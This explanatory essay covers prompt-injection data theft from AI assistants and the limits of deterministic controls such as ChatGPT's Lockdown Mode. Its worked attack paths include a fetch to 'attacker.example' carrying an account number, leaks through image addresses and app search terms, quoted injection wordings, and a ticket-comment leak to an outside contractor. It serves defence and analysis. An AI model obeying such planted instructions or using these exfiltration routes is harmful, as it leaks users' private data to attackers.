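# Limits of deterministic security guarantees against prompt-injection data theft in LLM systems

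## What is prompt-injection data theft, and what does a deterministic control add?

Prompt-injection data theft is an attack on software that uses a large language model (LLM), such as ChatGPT, Claude or Gemini. An attacker plants instructions in an email, web page or document that an assistant will later process for someone else. This planted text is called a prompt injection, and it works when the model follows it as a request instead of treating it as data. The assistant then sends that person's private data to the attacker, an unauthorized transfer called exfiltration.

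Vendors defend against the attack with probabilistic defences and deterministic controls. A probabilistic defence is a trained model or classifier that usually, but not always, resists or detects an injection. A deterministic control is a rule that ordinary software enforces in the same way whatever an attacker has got the model to do. One example is OpenAI's Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT, which limits outbound network requests. Private data can still get out even if such a rule never fails, because the data may travel by a route the rule does not cover.

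### How an email becomes a web request

An LLM takes in a sequence of tokens (words and pieces of words) and produces more tokens. Ordinary software turns the model into an assistant. The software builds the sequence from the vendor's standing instructions, the user's request, a list of available tools, and any files, emails or web pages the task involves. When the model produces a tool's name followed by its arguments in an agreed format, the software runs the tool, appends the result to the sequence and lets the model continue. A capability is anything the system can do beyond producing text, such as browsing, running code, showing a preview or calling an outside service.

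Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, works through a small case that contains everything an attack needs. Alice asks her assistant to summarise an email. The assistant holds her private account number and can fetch web pages, although this task gives it no reason to. The email comes from an attacker and contains an instruction to fetch a page from the attacker's site, with the account number added to the address. If the number is 40718825, the theft takes five steps:

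1. The software looks up the account number and makes it available to the model.
2. The software adds the text of the email to the model's sequence.
3. The model follows the instruction in the email and produces a call to the fetch tool, with the address `attacker.example/?d=40718825`.
4. The software runs the tool, which sends the attacker's server a request for that address.
5. The attacker reads the number in the server's log.

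The page does not have to exist. Websites use the part of an address after the question mark for details such as search terms and page numbers, and whoever makes the request chooses what to put there. A tool that seems only to retrieve information therefore also sends information out. Alice receives her summary and may see no sign that anything else happened.

In security research, a source is where private data enters the system, here the lookup of the account number. A sink is an action whose effect an attacker can observe, here the fetch. An outbound channel is any route, intended or not, by which information can leave the system. An attack path is the sequence of steps from the attacker's text to the attacker's goal.

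A human secretary would notice that Alice did not write the email, but the model has no dependable way to tell. Willison (2025) writes in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that "Everything eventually gets glued together into a sequence of tokens". The model follows instructions in that sequence whether or not they came from the person it works for. Willison, a software developer, named prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack in which a visitor types database commands into a web form and the software pastes them unchecked into a query that the database runs.

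Programmers prevent SQL injection with parameterised queries. They fix the structure of the query before supplying the user's text, so the database can only treat that text as a value. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore et al., 2026) explains why this method does not work for LLMs. A parser can use SQL's grammar to tell code from data, but natural language has no such grammar, and developers train models to follow instructions wherever they appear. A vendor can put markers around an email and tell the model to treat everything between them as data, but the protection depends on how well the model has learned to do so. The paper cites measurements by Zverev et al. in which neither prompting nor further training reliably produced a usable separation between instructions and data.

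Prompt injection differs from jailbreaking, in which the user tries to get forbidden output from the model. Alice is a user who has done nothing wrong, and she bears the loss. Willison complains that developers who confuse the two attacks dismiss prompt injection as a problem of embarrassing answers.

### The three conditions

According to Willison, the attack requires an assistant that has access to private data, can receive text that an attacker controls, and can communicate outward in a way that could transmit that data. Alice's assistant meets all three conditions through the account number, the email and the fetch tool, respectively.

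Removing any one of the three prevents the theft. Without the account number, the fetch carries nothing worth stealing. If the model reads no text from strangers, nobody tells it to make the fetch. Without the fetch tool or a substitute, the attacker receives no data even if the model follows the email's instructions completely.

The conditions apply to the assistant as a whole, so a user can meet them by accident when combining tools from different suppliers. A single tool can also meet all of them. Willison's example is a connector for GitHub, the code-hosting site. It could read public issues that anyone may file, read private code repositories, and create pull requests (proposed code changes) that could leak private material.

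Removing some of the three makes a system much less useful than removing others. An email assistant can do little for its owner if it can't read mail from strangers or access private data. Willison (2026) argues that the outbound route is by far the easiest to restrict without making the system much less useful. Vendors had been acting on roughly that view for years, responding to one report at a time. Willison lists products in which people had demonstrated this kind of theft, starting with ChatGPT in April 2023 and including Google Bard, Slack, GitHub Copilot Chat and about ten others. The vendors fixed almost all of the flaws promptly, usually by closing the route through which the data had left.

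Closing the outbound route does not remove the injection. OpenAI acknowledges in its help text for Lockdown Mode, quoted by Willison, that an injection in a cached page or an uploaded file "could still affect the behavior or accuracy of a response". The hostile email sent to Alice could no longer extract the account number through a fetch, but it could still put a false telephone number for her bank into the summary.

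### Why vendors do not rely on the model alone

If a model never obeyed the instructions in the email, no other control would be needed, and vendors do train their models to resist them. Researchers have also proposed many defences and reported very low attack success rates, but most of them tested a defence against a fixed list of known attack texts. A real attacker can study the defence and rewrite the text until it works.

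In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested twelve published defences, ten against prompt injection and two against jailbreaks, and let attackers adapt to them. The group included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. In their automated attacks, a program proposes wordings, tries them on the defended system, scores the results, and uses the scores to propose better ones. More than 500 people also attacked the defences by hand in an online contest the group ran.

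| Defence | How it is meant to work | Success of adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks untrusted text so that the model can tell it from instructions | above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | above 95% |
| StruQ | Trains the model on example attacks | every case tested |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model on example attacks | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | A separate detector screens the text | above 90% each |
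| PIGuard | A separate detector screens the text | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Tests whether the input distracts a model from repeating a secret key | every case tested |
| MELON | Runs the model twice and compares its tool calls | 76%; 95% if the attacker knows the design |
| RPO (jailbreaks) | Adds an optimised protective prompt | 96% to 98% |
| Circuit Breakers (jailbreaks) | Trains the model on example attacks | 100% |

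Attacks from fixed lists succeeded far less often. On AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office tasks with planted injections, the standard attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time against Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching, and MetaSecAlign's developers had reported a 2% success rate against it.

One successful attack text got past a detector by stating that a new company policy required staff to log every rescheduled meeting by deleting a certain temporary file. Nothing in it looks like an attack, and a detector strict enough to flag it would also flag a lot of ordinary office mail. Another text presented the malicious action as a step the assistant had to complete before it could do what the user wanted, which defeats a defence that reminds the model what the user wants. An attacker writing to Alice could similarly claim that the statement in the email will display properly only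 after the assistant has loaded a reference page.

These figures are for a strong attacker. Nasr and colleagues placed no tight limit on computing power, gave the search program the detectors' confidence scores, and tested each defence in isolation. They also warn against ranking the defences by these figures, because the test procedures differed. But the human contestants had only limited feedback, and on a selected set of scenarios they collectively succeeded in every one, while the automated search succeeded in 69%. An attacker who wants Alice's data can also open an account with the same vendor and practise the attack there. Nasr and colleagues acknowledge that detectors stop unsophisticated attacks, but a low attack success rate on a fixed list of attacks is poor evidence of how well a detector will stop an attacker who adapts.

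Attacks on the models themselves are also more likely to succeed when the attacker can try repeatedly. Narisetty and colleagues reproduce Anthropic's published results for its model Claude Opus 4.5 under adaptive attack in coding tasks. The attack success rate was 4.7% with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. If attempts were independent, each with success probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts would be 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ. With *p* = 0.047, that gives 38% for ten attempts and 99% for a hundred.

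The measured figures rise more slowly than they would if the attempts were independent and equally likely to succeed. Of the cases that withstood the first ten attempts, about 44% failed during the next ninety, or roughly 0.65% per attempt, compared with 4.7% initially. This is probably because the cases differ in difficulty, and those left after the early attempts are harder to break. Narisetty and colleagues describe a failure probability that "climbs toward certainty under repetition", which goes somewhat beyond these three numbers, since they do not show where the climb ends. Even so, a 63% failure rate is a serious problem for a defender. An attacker can also target many victims at once. At the single-attempt rate, an email that reached ten thousand such assistants would succeed 470 times on average.

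Results also depend heavily on what the assistant is doing. According to the news site VentureBeat, none of 200 attempts succeeded against Claude Opus 4.6 in a constrained coding environment in Anthropic's February 2026 tests. When the same model operated a graphical interface with extended reasoning switched on, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. The success rate by the 200th attempt was 78.6%, or 57.1% with additional safeguards.

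Newer models resist prompt injection better, though still imperfectly. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* benchmark embeds attacks in long office tasks such as analysing a bond portfolio. Attacks succeeded in 2.4% of cases against Gemini 4 Carbon, 4.3% against Gemini 4 Argon, 7.6% against GPT-6 Astra and 10.0% against Claude Fable 5.2. The margins of error are about two to four percentage points, too wide to rank neighbouring models reliably, but the differences across the whole field are much larger, with attacks succeeding in 91.4% of cases against Grok 4.5. PromptArmor sells AI security, so it has a commercial interest in showing that attacks work, and its figures include attacks with aims other than data theft, such as ransomware. It also states that no other known benchmark had produced a successful attack on Gemini 4 Carbon. If so, those benchmarks would have given a perfect score to a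 model that new attacks could still defeat.

A vendor's own results can be read in two ways. Anthropic reported that Claude Mythos 5 had the best result yet on an injection benchmark from Gray Swan, an external testing company. Simula's *CAISS analysis of Anthropics system card for Fable 5 and Mythos 5* concluded that the model and its safeguards had become less effective at blocking injections. Both can be true, because Anthropic also reported that Mythos 5 did better than one earlier model but worse than another on its coding and computer-use safety tests.

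OpenAI has said that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", which Narisetty and colleagues take as an admission about the model layer in general. Willison objects that vendors advertise filters that catch 95% of attacks, when in web security "95% is very much a failing grade". A web attacker can repeat an attempt with little effort and needs only one to succeed.

### A rule outside the model

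A deterministic control is designed on the assumption that the model will sometimes obey the attacker. The one Dongol adds to Alice's assistant is a runtime monitor, ordinary software that every tool call must pass through. The monitor disables the fetch tool as soon as the assistant reads untrusted content. When the model follows the email's instructions and produces the same call with the account number in the address, the monitor blocks it, and no request reaches the attacker's server.

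The monitor checks only which tool the model has called and whether the assistant has read anything untrusted. Its decision does not depend on how persuasive the email was or how the model explains the need for the fetch, so it blocks the hundredth attempt just as it blocked the first. In the formula for repeated attempts, *p* is therefore zero for this action, as long as the monitor's code is correct and the attacker cannot tamper with it.

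A defence can include fixed code and still be probabilistic. MELON, one of the twelve defences that Nasr and colleagues broke, runs the model once on the user's real request and once on a neutral request to summarise the same material. If the same tool call appears in both runs, MELON flags the material as containing an injection. Fixed code can make this comparison, but the result is still probabilistic because it depends on the model's behaviour, which the attacker's text influences in both runs. The successful attack told any system that was summarising to disregard the malicious instruction, so the suspicious call appeared only in the real run and the comparison found no match.

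There is much less evidence on how deterministic controls perform against adaptive attackers. Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent, a system that checks each tool call against a set of privilege rules. On AgentDojo, with a small open model as the agent, Progent reduced average attack success from 25.8% to 4.2%. An attack they wrote by hand with Progent in mind did no better, succeeding 2.6% of the time. They say these results are only consistent with such controls being harder targets, because they used one weak model and one attack template. Even if Progent enforced its rules perfectly, it would still let through an injection that asked for a call the rules permit, and a language model writes those rules.

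The control can also block legitimate work. Alice still gets her summary when the monitor withdraws the fetch tool, because summarising an email doesn't require it. But if she had asked the assistant to read the email and then send a reply, a monitor that withdrew the sending tool on the same principle would have blocked her task as well as the attacker's. Dongol observes that a monitor that refused every call would trivially pass the security test but be useless. Vendors therefore have a reason to leave some capabilities on, and each one needs to be examined as a possible route for data theft.

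### Enforcing a rule and guaranteeing an outcome

A guarantee that a rule always fires covers only the actions the rule names, while a guarantee that no data ever leaves must cover every action and side effect through which an outsider could learn something. The two are easy to confuse, especially in a product description.

Let *B* be the set of outbound channels that the rule blocks and *C* the set that the system actually has. If the rule always fires, every attempt to use a channel in *B* fails. This guarantees that no data leaves only if the rule blocks every channel the system has (*C* ⊆ *B*), since data could otherwise leave through an unblocked one.

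Suppose Alice's assistant can send email as well as fetch pages, but the monitor withdraws only the fetch tool. The attacker changes one sentence of the message so that it asks for a reply containing the account number. The model complies, and the software sends the number to the attacker, even though the monitor has refused every forbidden fetch. This is residual risk, the risk that remains when a control is on and works as designed, and no amount of testing the fetch rule would reveal it.

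Coverage also depends on timing, so a block on sending must be in place before the first untrusted text arrives. Dongol describes an assistant that reads an untrusted email, then reads a secret, and only then gives up its ability to send. The block is absolute once applied, but an injected instruction can make the assistant send the secret before then.

To show that a rule always fires, engineers can read and test a modest amount of code. To show that it covers every channel, they need a complete inventory of what the system can do, including effects that nobody designed as communication. Willison calls the ways a tool might carry data out "almost limitless" and mentions loading an image, or merely offering a link for the user to click. Since the 1970s, computer security has used the term "complete mediation" for the requirement that no access bypass the gate. A reference monitor, the classical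 form of such a gate, must meet this requirement, resist tampering, and be small enough to verify. A side channel can leak information as a by-product of some other operation, even if the gate correctly judges every request it receives. Narisetty and colleagues accordingly classify side channels as failures of mediation.

The model-level figures matter only on channels that the deterministic control overlooks. On a blocked channel, the monitor refuses the call whether the model obeys the attacker 2% of the time or 90%. On an open channel, the model's resistance to injection is the user's only protection, and the attacker again gains from every additional attempt. A vendor with a sound deterministic control therefore still has reason to train its models against injection. An attack success rate also cannot sum up the control's strength, because tests that all use the fetch tool would average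 zero even for an assistant that emails Alice's account number to a stranger.

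## What does ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode block, and what does OpenAI promise?

Lockdown Mode is an optional ChatGPT setting that turns off or restricts the features that let the assistant reach the web and outside services. OpenAI announced it on 13 February 2026 in *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. At first OpenAI offered it only on four plans for institutions: ChatGPT Enterprise, ChatGPT Edu, ChatGPT for Healthcare and ChatGPT for Teachers. An administrator creates a Lockdown Mode role and assigns people to it. The mode's restrictions add to any the administrator has already set.

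On 4 June 2026 OpenAI extended the mode to personal accounts, including free ones, and to Business accounts that customers set up themselves. That day's entry in OpenAI's *Release Notes* (2026) describes the mode as available to all logged-in users, but OpenAI's current help page, *Lockdown Mode*, says availability depends on the account, the workspace and the state of the rollout.

Some news sites mistook the June extension of Lockdown Mode for its launch. The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* presented the setting as new, and in November The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) gave June 2026 as its launch date. Privacy Guides' *ChatGPT Adds Lockdown Mode for Protection Against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026) had already described the mode on 21 February.

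The restrictions changed little between February and June, but OpenAI recommended the mode to a wider audience. In February, it aimed the mode at a "small set of highly security-conscious users", such as executives and security teams, and said that most people did not need it. In June, it recommended the mode to anyone who wanted a more conservative ChatGPT when working with sensitive information.

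### What each restriction closes

*Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (OpenAI, March 2026) explains the reasoning behind this kind of control. It compares an AI agent to a customer service worker who can issue refunds. The employer expects some customers to deceive the worker, so a separate system caps refunds to limit the loss when they succeed. Lockdown Mode similarly limits the ways ChatGPT can send information out.

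OpenAI's help page lists the restricted features. The channels in the right-hand column below follow from how each feature works.

| Feature | In Lockdown Mode | Outbound channel closed |
|---|---|---|
| Live web browsing | ChatGPT reads only stored copies of pages | Requests to outside websites, whose addresses can carry data |
| Images in answers | ChatGPT may not display images in ordinary answers or retrieve them from the web | Requests for image files, which can go out without a click |
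| Deep research | Off | The many searches and page visits that go into a research report |
| Agent mode | Off | Page visits, and anything the agent types or submits on a website |
| Canvas networking | Users cannot approve network access for code generated in Canvas | Requests made by running code |
| File downloads | ChatGPT cannot download files for data analysis | Requests for a file at an address the model supplies |

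The image restriction covers a route that a limit on browsing would miss. A chat answer can contain the address of an image, which the user's own app then requests to display it. An injection could have the model write an image address that ends in Alice's account number, and her laptop would send the number to the attacker when it requested the image. The security researcher Johann Rehberger reported an attack of this type to OpenAI in early 2023. He recounts in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that OpenAI introduced a check on addresses that December, but that the macOS and iOS apps lacked it for a time.

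OpenAI's wording leaves some doubt about whether the mode fully blocks this route. According to the help page, ChatGPT "may not display" images, which could mean that it never displays them or that it sometimes doesn't. The June release note refers to restrictions on "some web-derived image support".

The deep research feature searches and reads many sources, then writes a report. It can draw on a user's private mail as well as the web, so a single task can include both the source and the sink. OpenAI reproduces a 2025 attack of this kind, reported by outside researchers. The attacker's email looked like a follow-up to a meeting about staff restructuring. It told the assistant to find an employee's name and address in another message and submit them to a "compliance validation system", and claimed the assistant was fully authorised to do so. When the user asked for deep research on that day's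 emails about the new-employee process, the attack worked 50% of the time in testing. Lockdown Mode removes deep research, so such an email can't hijack a deep research task.

Agent mode lets ChatGPT operate websites for the user. An agent that can fill in a form can put private data into it, so checking web addresses alone would not be enough to prevent data theft.

Lockdown Mode stops users from approving unexpected communication by code in Canvas, ChatGPT's workspace for writing documents and code. The code runs in a sandbox, an isolated environment that detects such communication and normally asks the user for consent. Removing that choice makes the control stricter, because people approve requests they should refuse. OpenAI warned in January that frequent false alarms about links can train people to click through without thinking.

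A list of named features needs updating as the product changes. On 28 May 2026, a week before it extended Lockdown Mode to personal accounts, OpenAI withdrew Canvas from the GPT-5.5 Instant and GPT-5.5 Thinking models and moved Canvas's writing and coding functions into blocks inside the chat. The change did not necessarily open a new channel for data theft, but new places to display and run code need their own rules. The bypass that The Hacker News covered in November, which OpenAI had fixed on 18 September, used the web page preview in code blocks.

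### Why cached browsing sends no request to the attacker

ChatGPT checks web addresses even when Lockdown Mode is off. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a crawler, a program that records public web addresses and has no access to anyone's conversations. Before ChatGPT opens an address automatically, software checks whether the crawler has already recorded that exact address. The crawler would not have recorded `attacker.example/?d=40718825`, which contains Alice's account number, so ChatGPT would try a different website or warn Alice and let her decide whether to open the address.

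OpenAI considered relying on a list of trusted websites but found it too weak, because many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a link could start at a trusted site and end at an attacker's. Checking whether the full address was public before the conversation is a better test, since such an address is unlikely to contain a secret from the conversation.

The default check still lets ChatGPT make live requests to addresses that pass. If an attacker owns one of those pages, their server records the visit. Rehberger points out that the connection itself can leak a little information, even when the address contains no private text. The check therefore makes theft through web addresses harder but doesn't rule it out.

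Lockdown Mode replaces the live request with a lookup in a cache, a store of copies saved earlier. If Alice's assistant used cached browsing, the attack from the previous section would go as follows:

1. OpenAI saves copies of public web pages, independently of Alice's conversation. The attacker's server may receive a request at this stage, but the request contains nothing about her.
2. Alice's assistant reads the hostile email, and the model calls the browsing tool with the account number in the address.
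3. The software looks for a saved copy under that address, inside OpenAI's own network.
4. It finds none, because no such page was ever public. The model receives no page, and the attacker's server receives no request.
5. If the model asks instead for one of the attacker's pages that is in the cache, the software returns the saved copy. The attacker's server still receives no request and has no record that anyone read the page.

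The outcome is the same even if the model fails completely in step 2. The lookup also removes the small leak that remains under the default check, because the attacker can't observe which saved pages the model reads.

This argument holds only if the assistant's requests have no effect on what OpenAI saves. Suppose the software responded to a failed lookup by adding the missing address to a list of pages to fetch later. The attacker would then receive the account number when OpenAI fetched the page. OpenAI's February announcement rules out an immediate fetch, since it says that "no live network requests leave OpenAI's controlled network" through browsing, but it does not explain how OpenAI chooses pages for the cache.

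OpenAI warns that search results in Lockdown Mode may be limited, unavailable or out of date, so a user may not get today's exchange rate or a notice posted on a website an hour ago.

### What stays as it was

Lockdown Mode restricts sinks but leaves most sources in place. File uploads work as before, and so does ChatGPT's memory, which carries information from one conversation to another. On the day OpenAI extended the mode to personal accounts, it also began rolling out a memory upgrade that doubled the capacity for Plus and Pro subscribers. ChatGPT can therefore hold more private information about someone who turns on Lockdown Mode than it did a month earlier. This is consistent with the design, which tries to stop information from leaving ChatGPT and does not reduce how much it holds.

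In Lockdown Mode, users can still share conversations and generate images. The mode does not change whether OpenAI may use conversations to improve its models, because a separate setting controls that.

On personal and self-serve accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks many functions of apps, the outside services that users connect to ChatGPT. In managed workspaces, administrators decide which ones to allow. The Next Web reported in June that turning on either Lockdown Mode or Developer Mode disabled the other.

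Lockdown Mode does not affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding assistant. Codex has separate settings that let a developer give it internet access and limit that access to chosen sites and types of request. If a company turns on Lockdown Mode to protect unreleased software, the mode does not protect that software when developers open it in Codex.

A user can also turn the mode off for a single chat. On the web, the user selects the Lockdown Mode label beside the message box and then "Turn off for this chat". Other chats keep their restrictions, so a user who needs one live web page does not have to give up the protection everywhere.

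Switching live browsing back on is riskier in the middle of a conversation than at the beginning. By then the model may have read both a private file and a hostile document, and both remain in the conversation. An injection could also try to get the user to make the switch by having ChatGPT say that it can't finish the task without live access. The rule would still work as designed, but the user would be lifting it because of an answer the injection had distorted.

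Lockdown Mode does not stop prompt injections from reaching the model, so they can still distort its answers in any chat. For example, a supplier could hide text in a contract that makes ChatGPT omit a penalty clause from its summary. The customer could then lose money even though no data leaked.

### What the promise means

OpenAI's main promise, on its help page, is that Lockdown Mode is "designed to substantially reduce the risk" of data exfiltration through prompt injection, but it "does not guarantee data exfiltration cannot happen".

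By saying "designed to", OpenAI states an aim but reports no result. It limits the promise to "prompt injection-based" theft, which excludes other kinds, such as an intruder logging in with a stolen password. The promise covers ChatGPT and "supported OpenAI products", though OpenAI exempts network access in Codex on the same page.

"Substantially reduce" is relative to ChatGPT with the mode off. In its announcement, release notes and help page, OpenAI has given no figure for the reduction. It has also not said whether it would measure the reduction by the share of test attacks that fail, the number of real thefts or the amount of data lost.

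A figure would be hard to interpret even if OpenAI published one, because the overall reduction depends on how attackers divide their efforts between blocked and open channels. If *r*(*c*) is the number of thefts expected through channel *c* with the mode off, and *B* and *C* are again the blocked channels and all channels, the mode reduces thefts by this fraction:

Σ *r*(*c*) over the channels in *B* ÷ Σ *r*(*c*) over the channels in *C*

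The formula assumes that attackers do not change their methods. Suppose, for illustration, that 100 thefts would occur with the mode off, 90 of them through channels it blocks. If nobody adapts, the mode prevents 90%. If attackers can carry out 30 of those 90 thefts through a channel that is still open, 40 thefts remain and the mode prevents only 60%. A vendor therefore can't work out the benefit from past attacks alone.

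A useful test of Lockdown Mode would start with attacks that succeed without it. In *The Framing Gap* (2026), an outside test of data theft by injection, ChatGPT leaked the secret in none of 48 valid trials, while a model accessed through the developer interface leaked it in up to 100%. The researchers could not see inside the product and did not attribute the difference to any particular protection. The test did not measure Lockdown Mode, but if ChatGPT resists every attack in a test with the mode off, turning it on cannot improve the score. Zero leaks in 48 trials also does not prove that ChatGPT is safe, since a true leak rate of about 6% would still produce that result one time in twenty.

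OpenAI uses the words "does not guarantee," so it is not promising that no data can ever leave. It names three places where risk may remain, and they differ in what a customer can do about them.

Enabled apps are a known route for data theft. An administrator who lets ChatGPT write to an outside service accepts that an attack could send data there, and can close that route by withdrawing the permission.

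"Unforeseen combinations of capabilities" refers to attacks that combine several features, each of which looks safe on its own. A customer cannot switch off a combination that nobody has identified, so the only precaution is to leave fewer features on, which gives an attacker fewer to combine.

The disclaimer's phrase "newly discovered techniques" covers methods that nobody had thought of when OpenAI chose the restrictions, including ways around those restrictions. Customers depend on OpenAI to respond to such methods, because only OpenAI can repair its own software. OpenAI could keep this part of the disclaimer indefinitely, however many repairs it makes.

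OpenAI described Lockdown Mode in stronger terms in February than it does now. It announced then that the mode "deterministically disables certain tools and capabilities", and that it turns some features off entirely when it cannot provide "strong deterministic guarantees of data safety". Privacy Guides quotes another passage from that time, in which OpenAI described the mode as "deterministically preventing outbound network requests" that could carry data to an attacker. On the current help page, OpenAI says "limiting" instead of "preventing" and does not use the word "deterministic". OpenAI had adopted the softer wording by 5 June, when Willison quoted it.

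The change is smaller than it looks. The phrase about strong guarantees explains why OpenAI disabled individual features. It implies that OpenAI saw a firm basis for leaving others on in restricted form, most clearly cached browsing, but it does not apply to the product as a whole. Privacy Guides also reported in February that OpenAI claimed only to greatly reduce the risk, not to eliminate it. OpenAI has not explained the edit. The newer wording is more accurate, because the mode lets administrators keep apps connected and so limits outbound requests without preventing all of them.

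Some press coverage overstated what OpenAI promised. The Decoder's *ChatGPT's new Lockdown Mode lets you disable web access and more* states that the feature blocks all connections to the internet and external services. But administrators can leave apps on, and a reader who believed the article would have no reason to check which ones.

### Who needs the mode

Willison wrote of the June release, "This looks really good to me" (*OpenAI Help*, 2026). He liked that it targets the outbound route with deterministic mechanisms that don't rely on evaluation by an AI system, which a sufficiently devious injection could fool. He was praising the type of control, based on OpenAI's description rather than a test of the product.

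Willison also inferred that if some users need Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT without it must lack a robust defence against a determined data thief. This does not strictly follow, since a company may add another layer to a system that is already strong, but OpenAI's own account of the default protections supports him. In March, it wrote that most of the attacks it knew of fail because its safety training leads the model to refuse. When the model does not refuse, ChatGPT blocks the transmission or asks the user to confirm it. The model's refusals are probabilistic, and a user who is asked to confirm can be deceived. OpenAI also conceded in the February announcement that existing safeguards across the industry do not yet fully address the risks of some network features.

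Willison later updated his article with a post by Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's chief information security officer. Stuckey wrote that the mode is "not meant for everyone" and suits people whose risk is higher because of who they are, what they work on or what data they handle. He considered the loss of functionality worthwhile for them. In the post, he did not address Willison's point about the defaults.

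The two positions are compatible. An attack that rarely succeeds may be an acceptable risk for someone planning a holiday but not for a lawyer with a client's merger documents. But Stuckey's advice requires people to judge their own exposure, which can change quickly, such as when someone who normally asks for recipes uploads a tax return. OpenAI allowed for this in June by also recommending the mode for moments when a user is willing to give up features for stricter protection.

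In the same February announcement, OpenAI introduced "Elevated Risk" labels for people who leave the mode off. The labels mark a short list of existing features in ChatGPT, Codex and OpenAI's web browser, ChatGPT Atlas, but don't block anything. In Codex, for example, the label appears on the screen where a developer grants internet access, with an explanation of what the setting changes, what risks it brings and when it is appropriate. OpenAI plans to remove the label from a feature once it decides that better security has reduced the risk enough for general use, but it has not published a threshold for that decision.

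## How can an enabled app still carry data out?

OpenAI lists enabled apps, such as a mailbox or a company's ticket tracker, first among the places where it warns that risk may remain in Lockdown Mode. These apps hold the private data an attacker wants, and some let the assistant write where an outsider can read. A mail app also brings in text from strangers. Together, a few connected apps can therefore meet all three of Willison's conditions without any request to an attacker's website.

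In *Data exfiltration in OpenAI agent*, PromptArmor demonstrated such a theft on a chain of agents. One agent collected a response to a form, and another fetched recently updated contacts from the customer database Salesforce. A third agent received both, followed an instruction hidden in the form response, and emailed the customer data to the attacker. ZombieAgent, an attack on ChatGPT, also worked through connected apps.

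### Who decides which apps stay on

On personal and self-serve Business accounts, Lockdown Mode largely determines which app features work. It blocks live access to outside services and actions that write to an app when these conflict with its protections. It disables the personal finance feature and the shopping agents completely. In June, Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks* reported that these users could still search app data that OpenAI had already copied, because searching it sends no live request. OpenAI's current help page no longer mentions that exception.

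OpenAI lets administrators of managed workspaces choose which apps, and which actions within them, are available in Lockdown Mode because "some critical workflows rely on apps". Two people with Lockdown Mode on can therefore have very different exposure to data theft. One person's assistant may be cut off from nearly every outside service, while the other's can read company mail and post to a ticket tracker.

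According to OpenAI's *Admin controls, security, and compliance for plugins and apps*, new Enterprise and Edu workspaces start with selected apps enabled. Administrators can usually allow reading and writing separately, but some apps lack that control.

Apps also gain new actions over time. According to OpenAI's *App Security Whitepaper* (2026), when an administrator selects both read and write actions for an app, ChatGPT also selects a setting that enables future actions automatically. If the administrator leaves that setting on, new actions become available without the administrator's review. The administrator can instead keep new actions off until someone has checked them.

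### What each kind of access exposes

OpenAI gives administrators a risk rating for each kind of app access. The last two columns below apply the terms source and sink to each kind.

| Access | OpenAI's rating | Source of private data? | Sink an attacker could observe? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading or writing in an untrusted app | High | Yes, if the app holds private data | Yes, the app's operator receives each request |
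| Writing in a trusted app, with broad or uncertain visibility | High | Not usually | Yes, for anyone who can see the result |
| Writing in a trusted app, with limited visibility | Medium | Not usually | Only for the people who can see the result |
| Reading in a trusted app | Medium | Yes | Weakly, since the provider receives the search terms but other people see no change |
| Searching sources that administrators have indexed | Medium | Yes | Hardly, since the search uses an existing copy |

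An app that can only read data can still carry data out, because the model writes the search terms it sends to the app. Embrace The Red's *How Deep Research Agents Can Leak Your Data* describes how Rehberger tested this with his own app. OpenAI required such apps to offer exactly two functions, search and fetch, so his app had no function for writing anything. He connected it to ChatGPT alongside Linear, a ticket tracker, and asked for a table of open issues. To provoke a leak, he planted instructions in the tickets and in his app's description. ChatGPT then sent sensitive details from the tickets to his server as search terms. In one query it combined the name of a production service with login credentials, which it had gathered from several tickets.

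Rehberger used deep research, which Lockdown Mode turns off, but an ordinary search in an app also sends the search terms to the app's operator. OpenAI does not verify custom apps, which customers or other developers connect themselves, and it tells organisations to treat any data sent to a custom app's server as shared externally. OpenAI also notes that an app receives only what a particular request contains and has no general access to a user's memories. This limits accidental sharing but protects less against an injection, which can influence what the model puts in the request.

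A trusted provider also receives search terms, but the risk is lower because an outside attacker normally cannot read a large mail provider's logs. A trusted app can still let an injection in, because a reliable mail service will deliver a hostile email like any other.

The risk of a write action depends on who can see its result. OpenAI advises against enabling write actions unless the administrator can confirm that a malicious actor cannot see the effect. This can be hard to confirm because visibility depends on the connected app's guest accounts, public links and notification settings. Many ticket trackers email each new comment to everyone following the ticket, and deleting the comment does not recall those emails.

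With indexed sources, the assistant searches a copy instead of sending the provider a live request. These sources can still supply private data that another app then leaks. They may also be hard to get. OpenAI's help page for Lockdown Mode still rates them, but according to its page for administrators, administrator-managed sync is no longer available.

### A contract price in a ticket

Suppose Alice's employer has given her a Lockdown Mode role. Her administrator has enabled read actions in the mail app and the company wiki, and read and write actions in the ticket tracker. Only employees used the tracker when the administrator reviewed it, so its write actions counted as limited in visibility. Since then, a project lead has invited Victor, an outside contractor, to a project about an office move. Victor wants to know what the company pays his competitor, and that price is on a wiki page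 open to all staff.

1. Victor emails Alice about ticket 212. Near the end, he writes that the finance department now requires each update to quote the current price from the wiki's supplier page.
2. Alice asks ChatGPT to go through the morning's mail and bring the tickets up to date.
3. The mail app returns Victor's message. Alice has the right to read her own mail.
4. The model follows the instruction and searches the wiki, which returns a page giving the price as $184,000. Alice has the right to read that page.
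5. The model produces a comment for ticket 212 containing a new delivery date and the price. Alice has the right to comment there. If ChatGPT asks her to approve the comment, she does.
6. Victor opens ticket 212, which he has the right to read, and finds the price.

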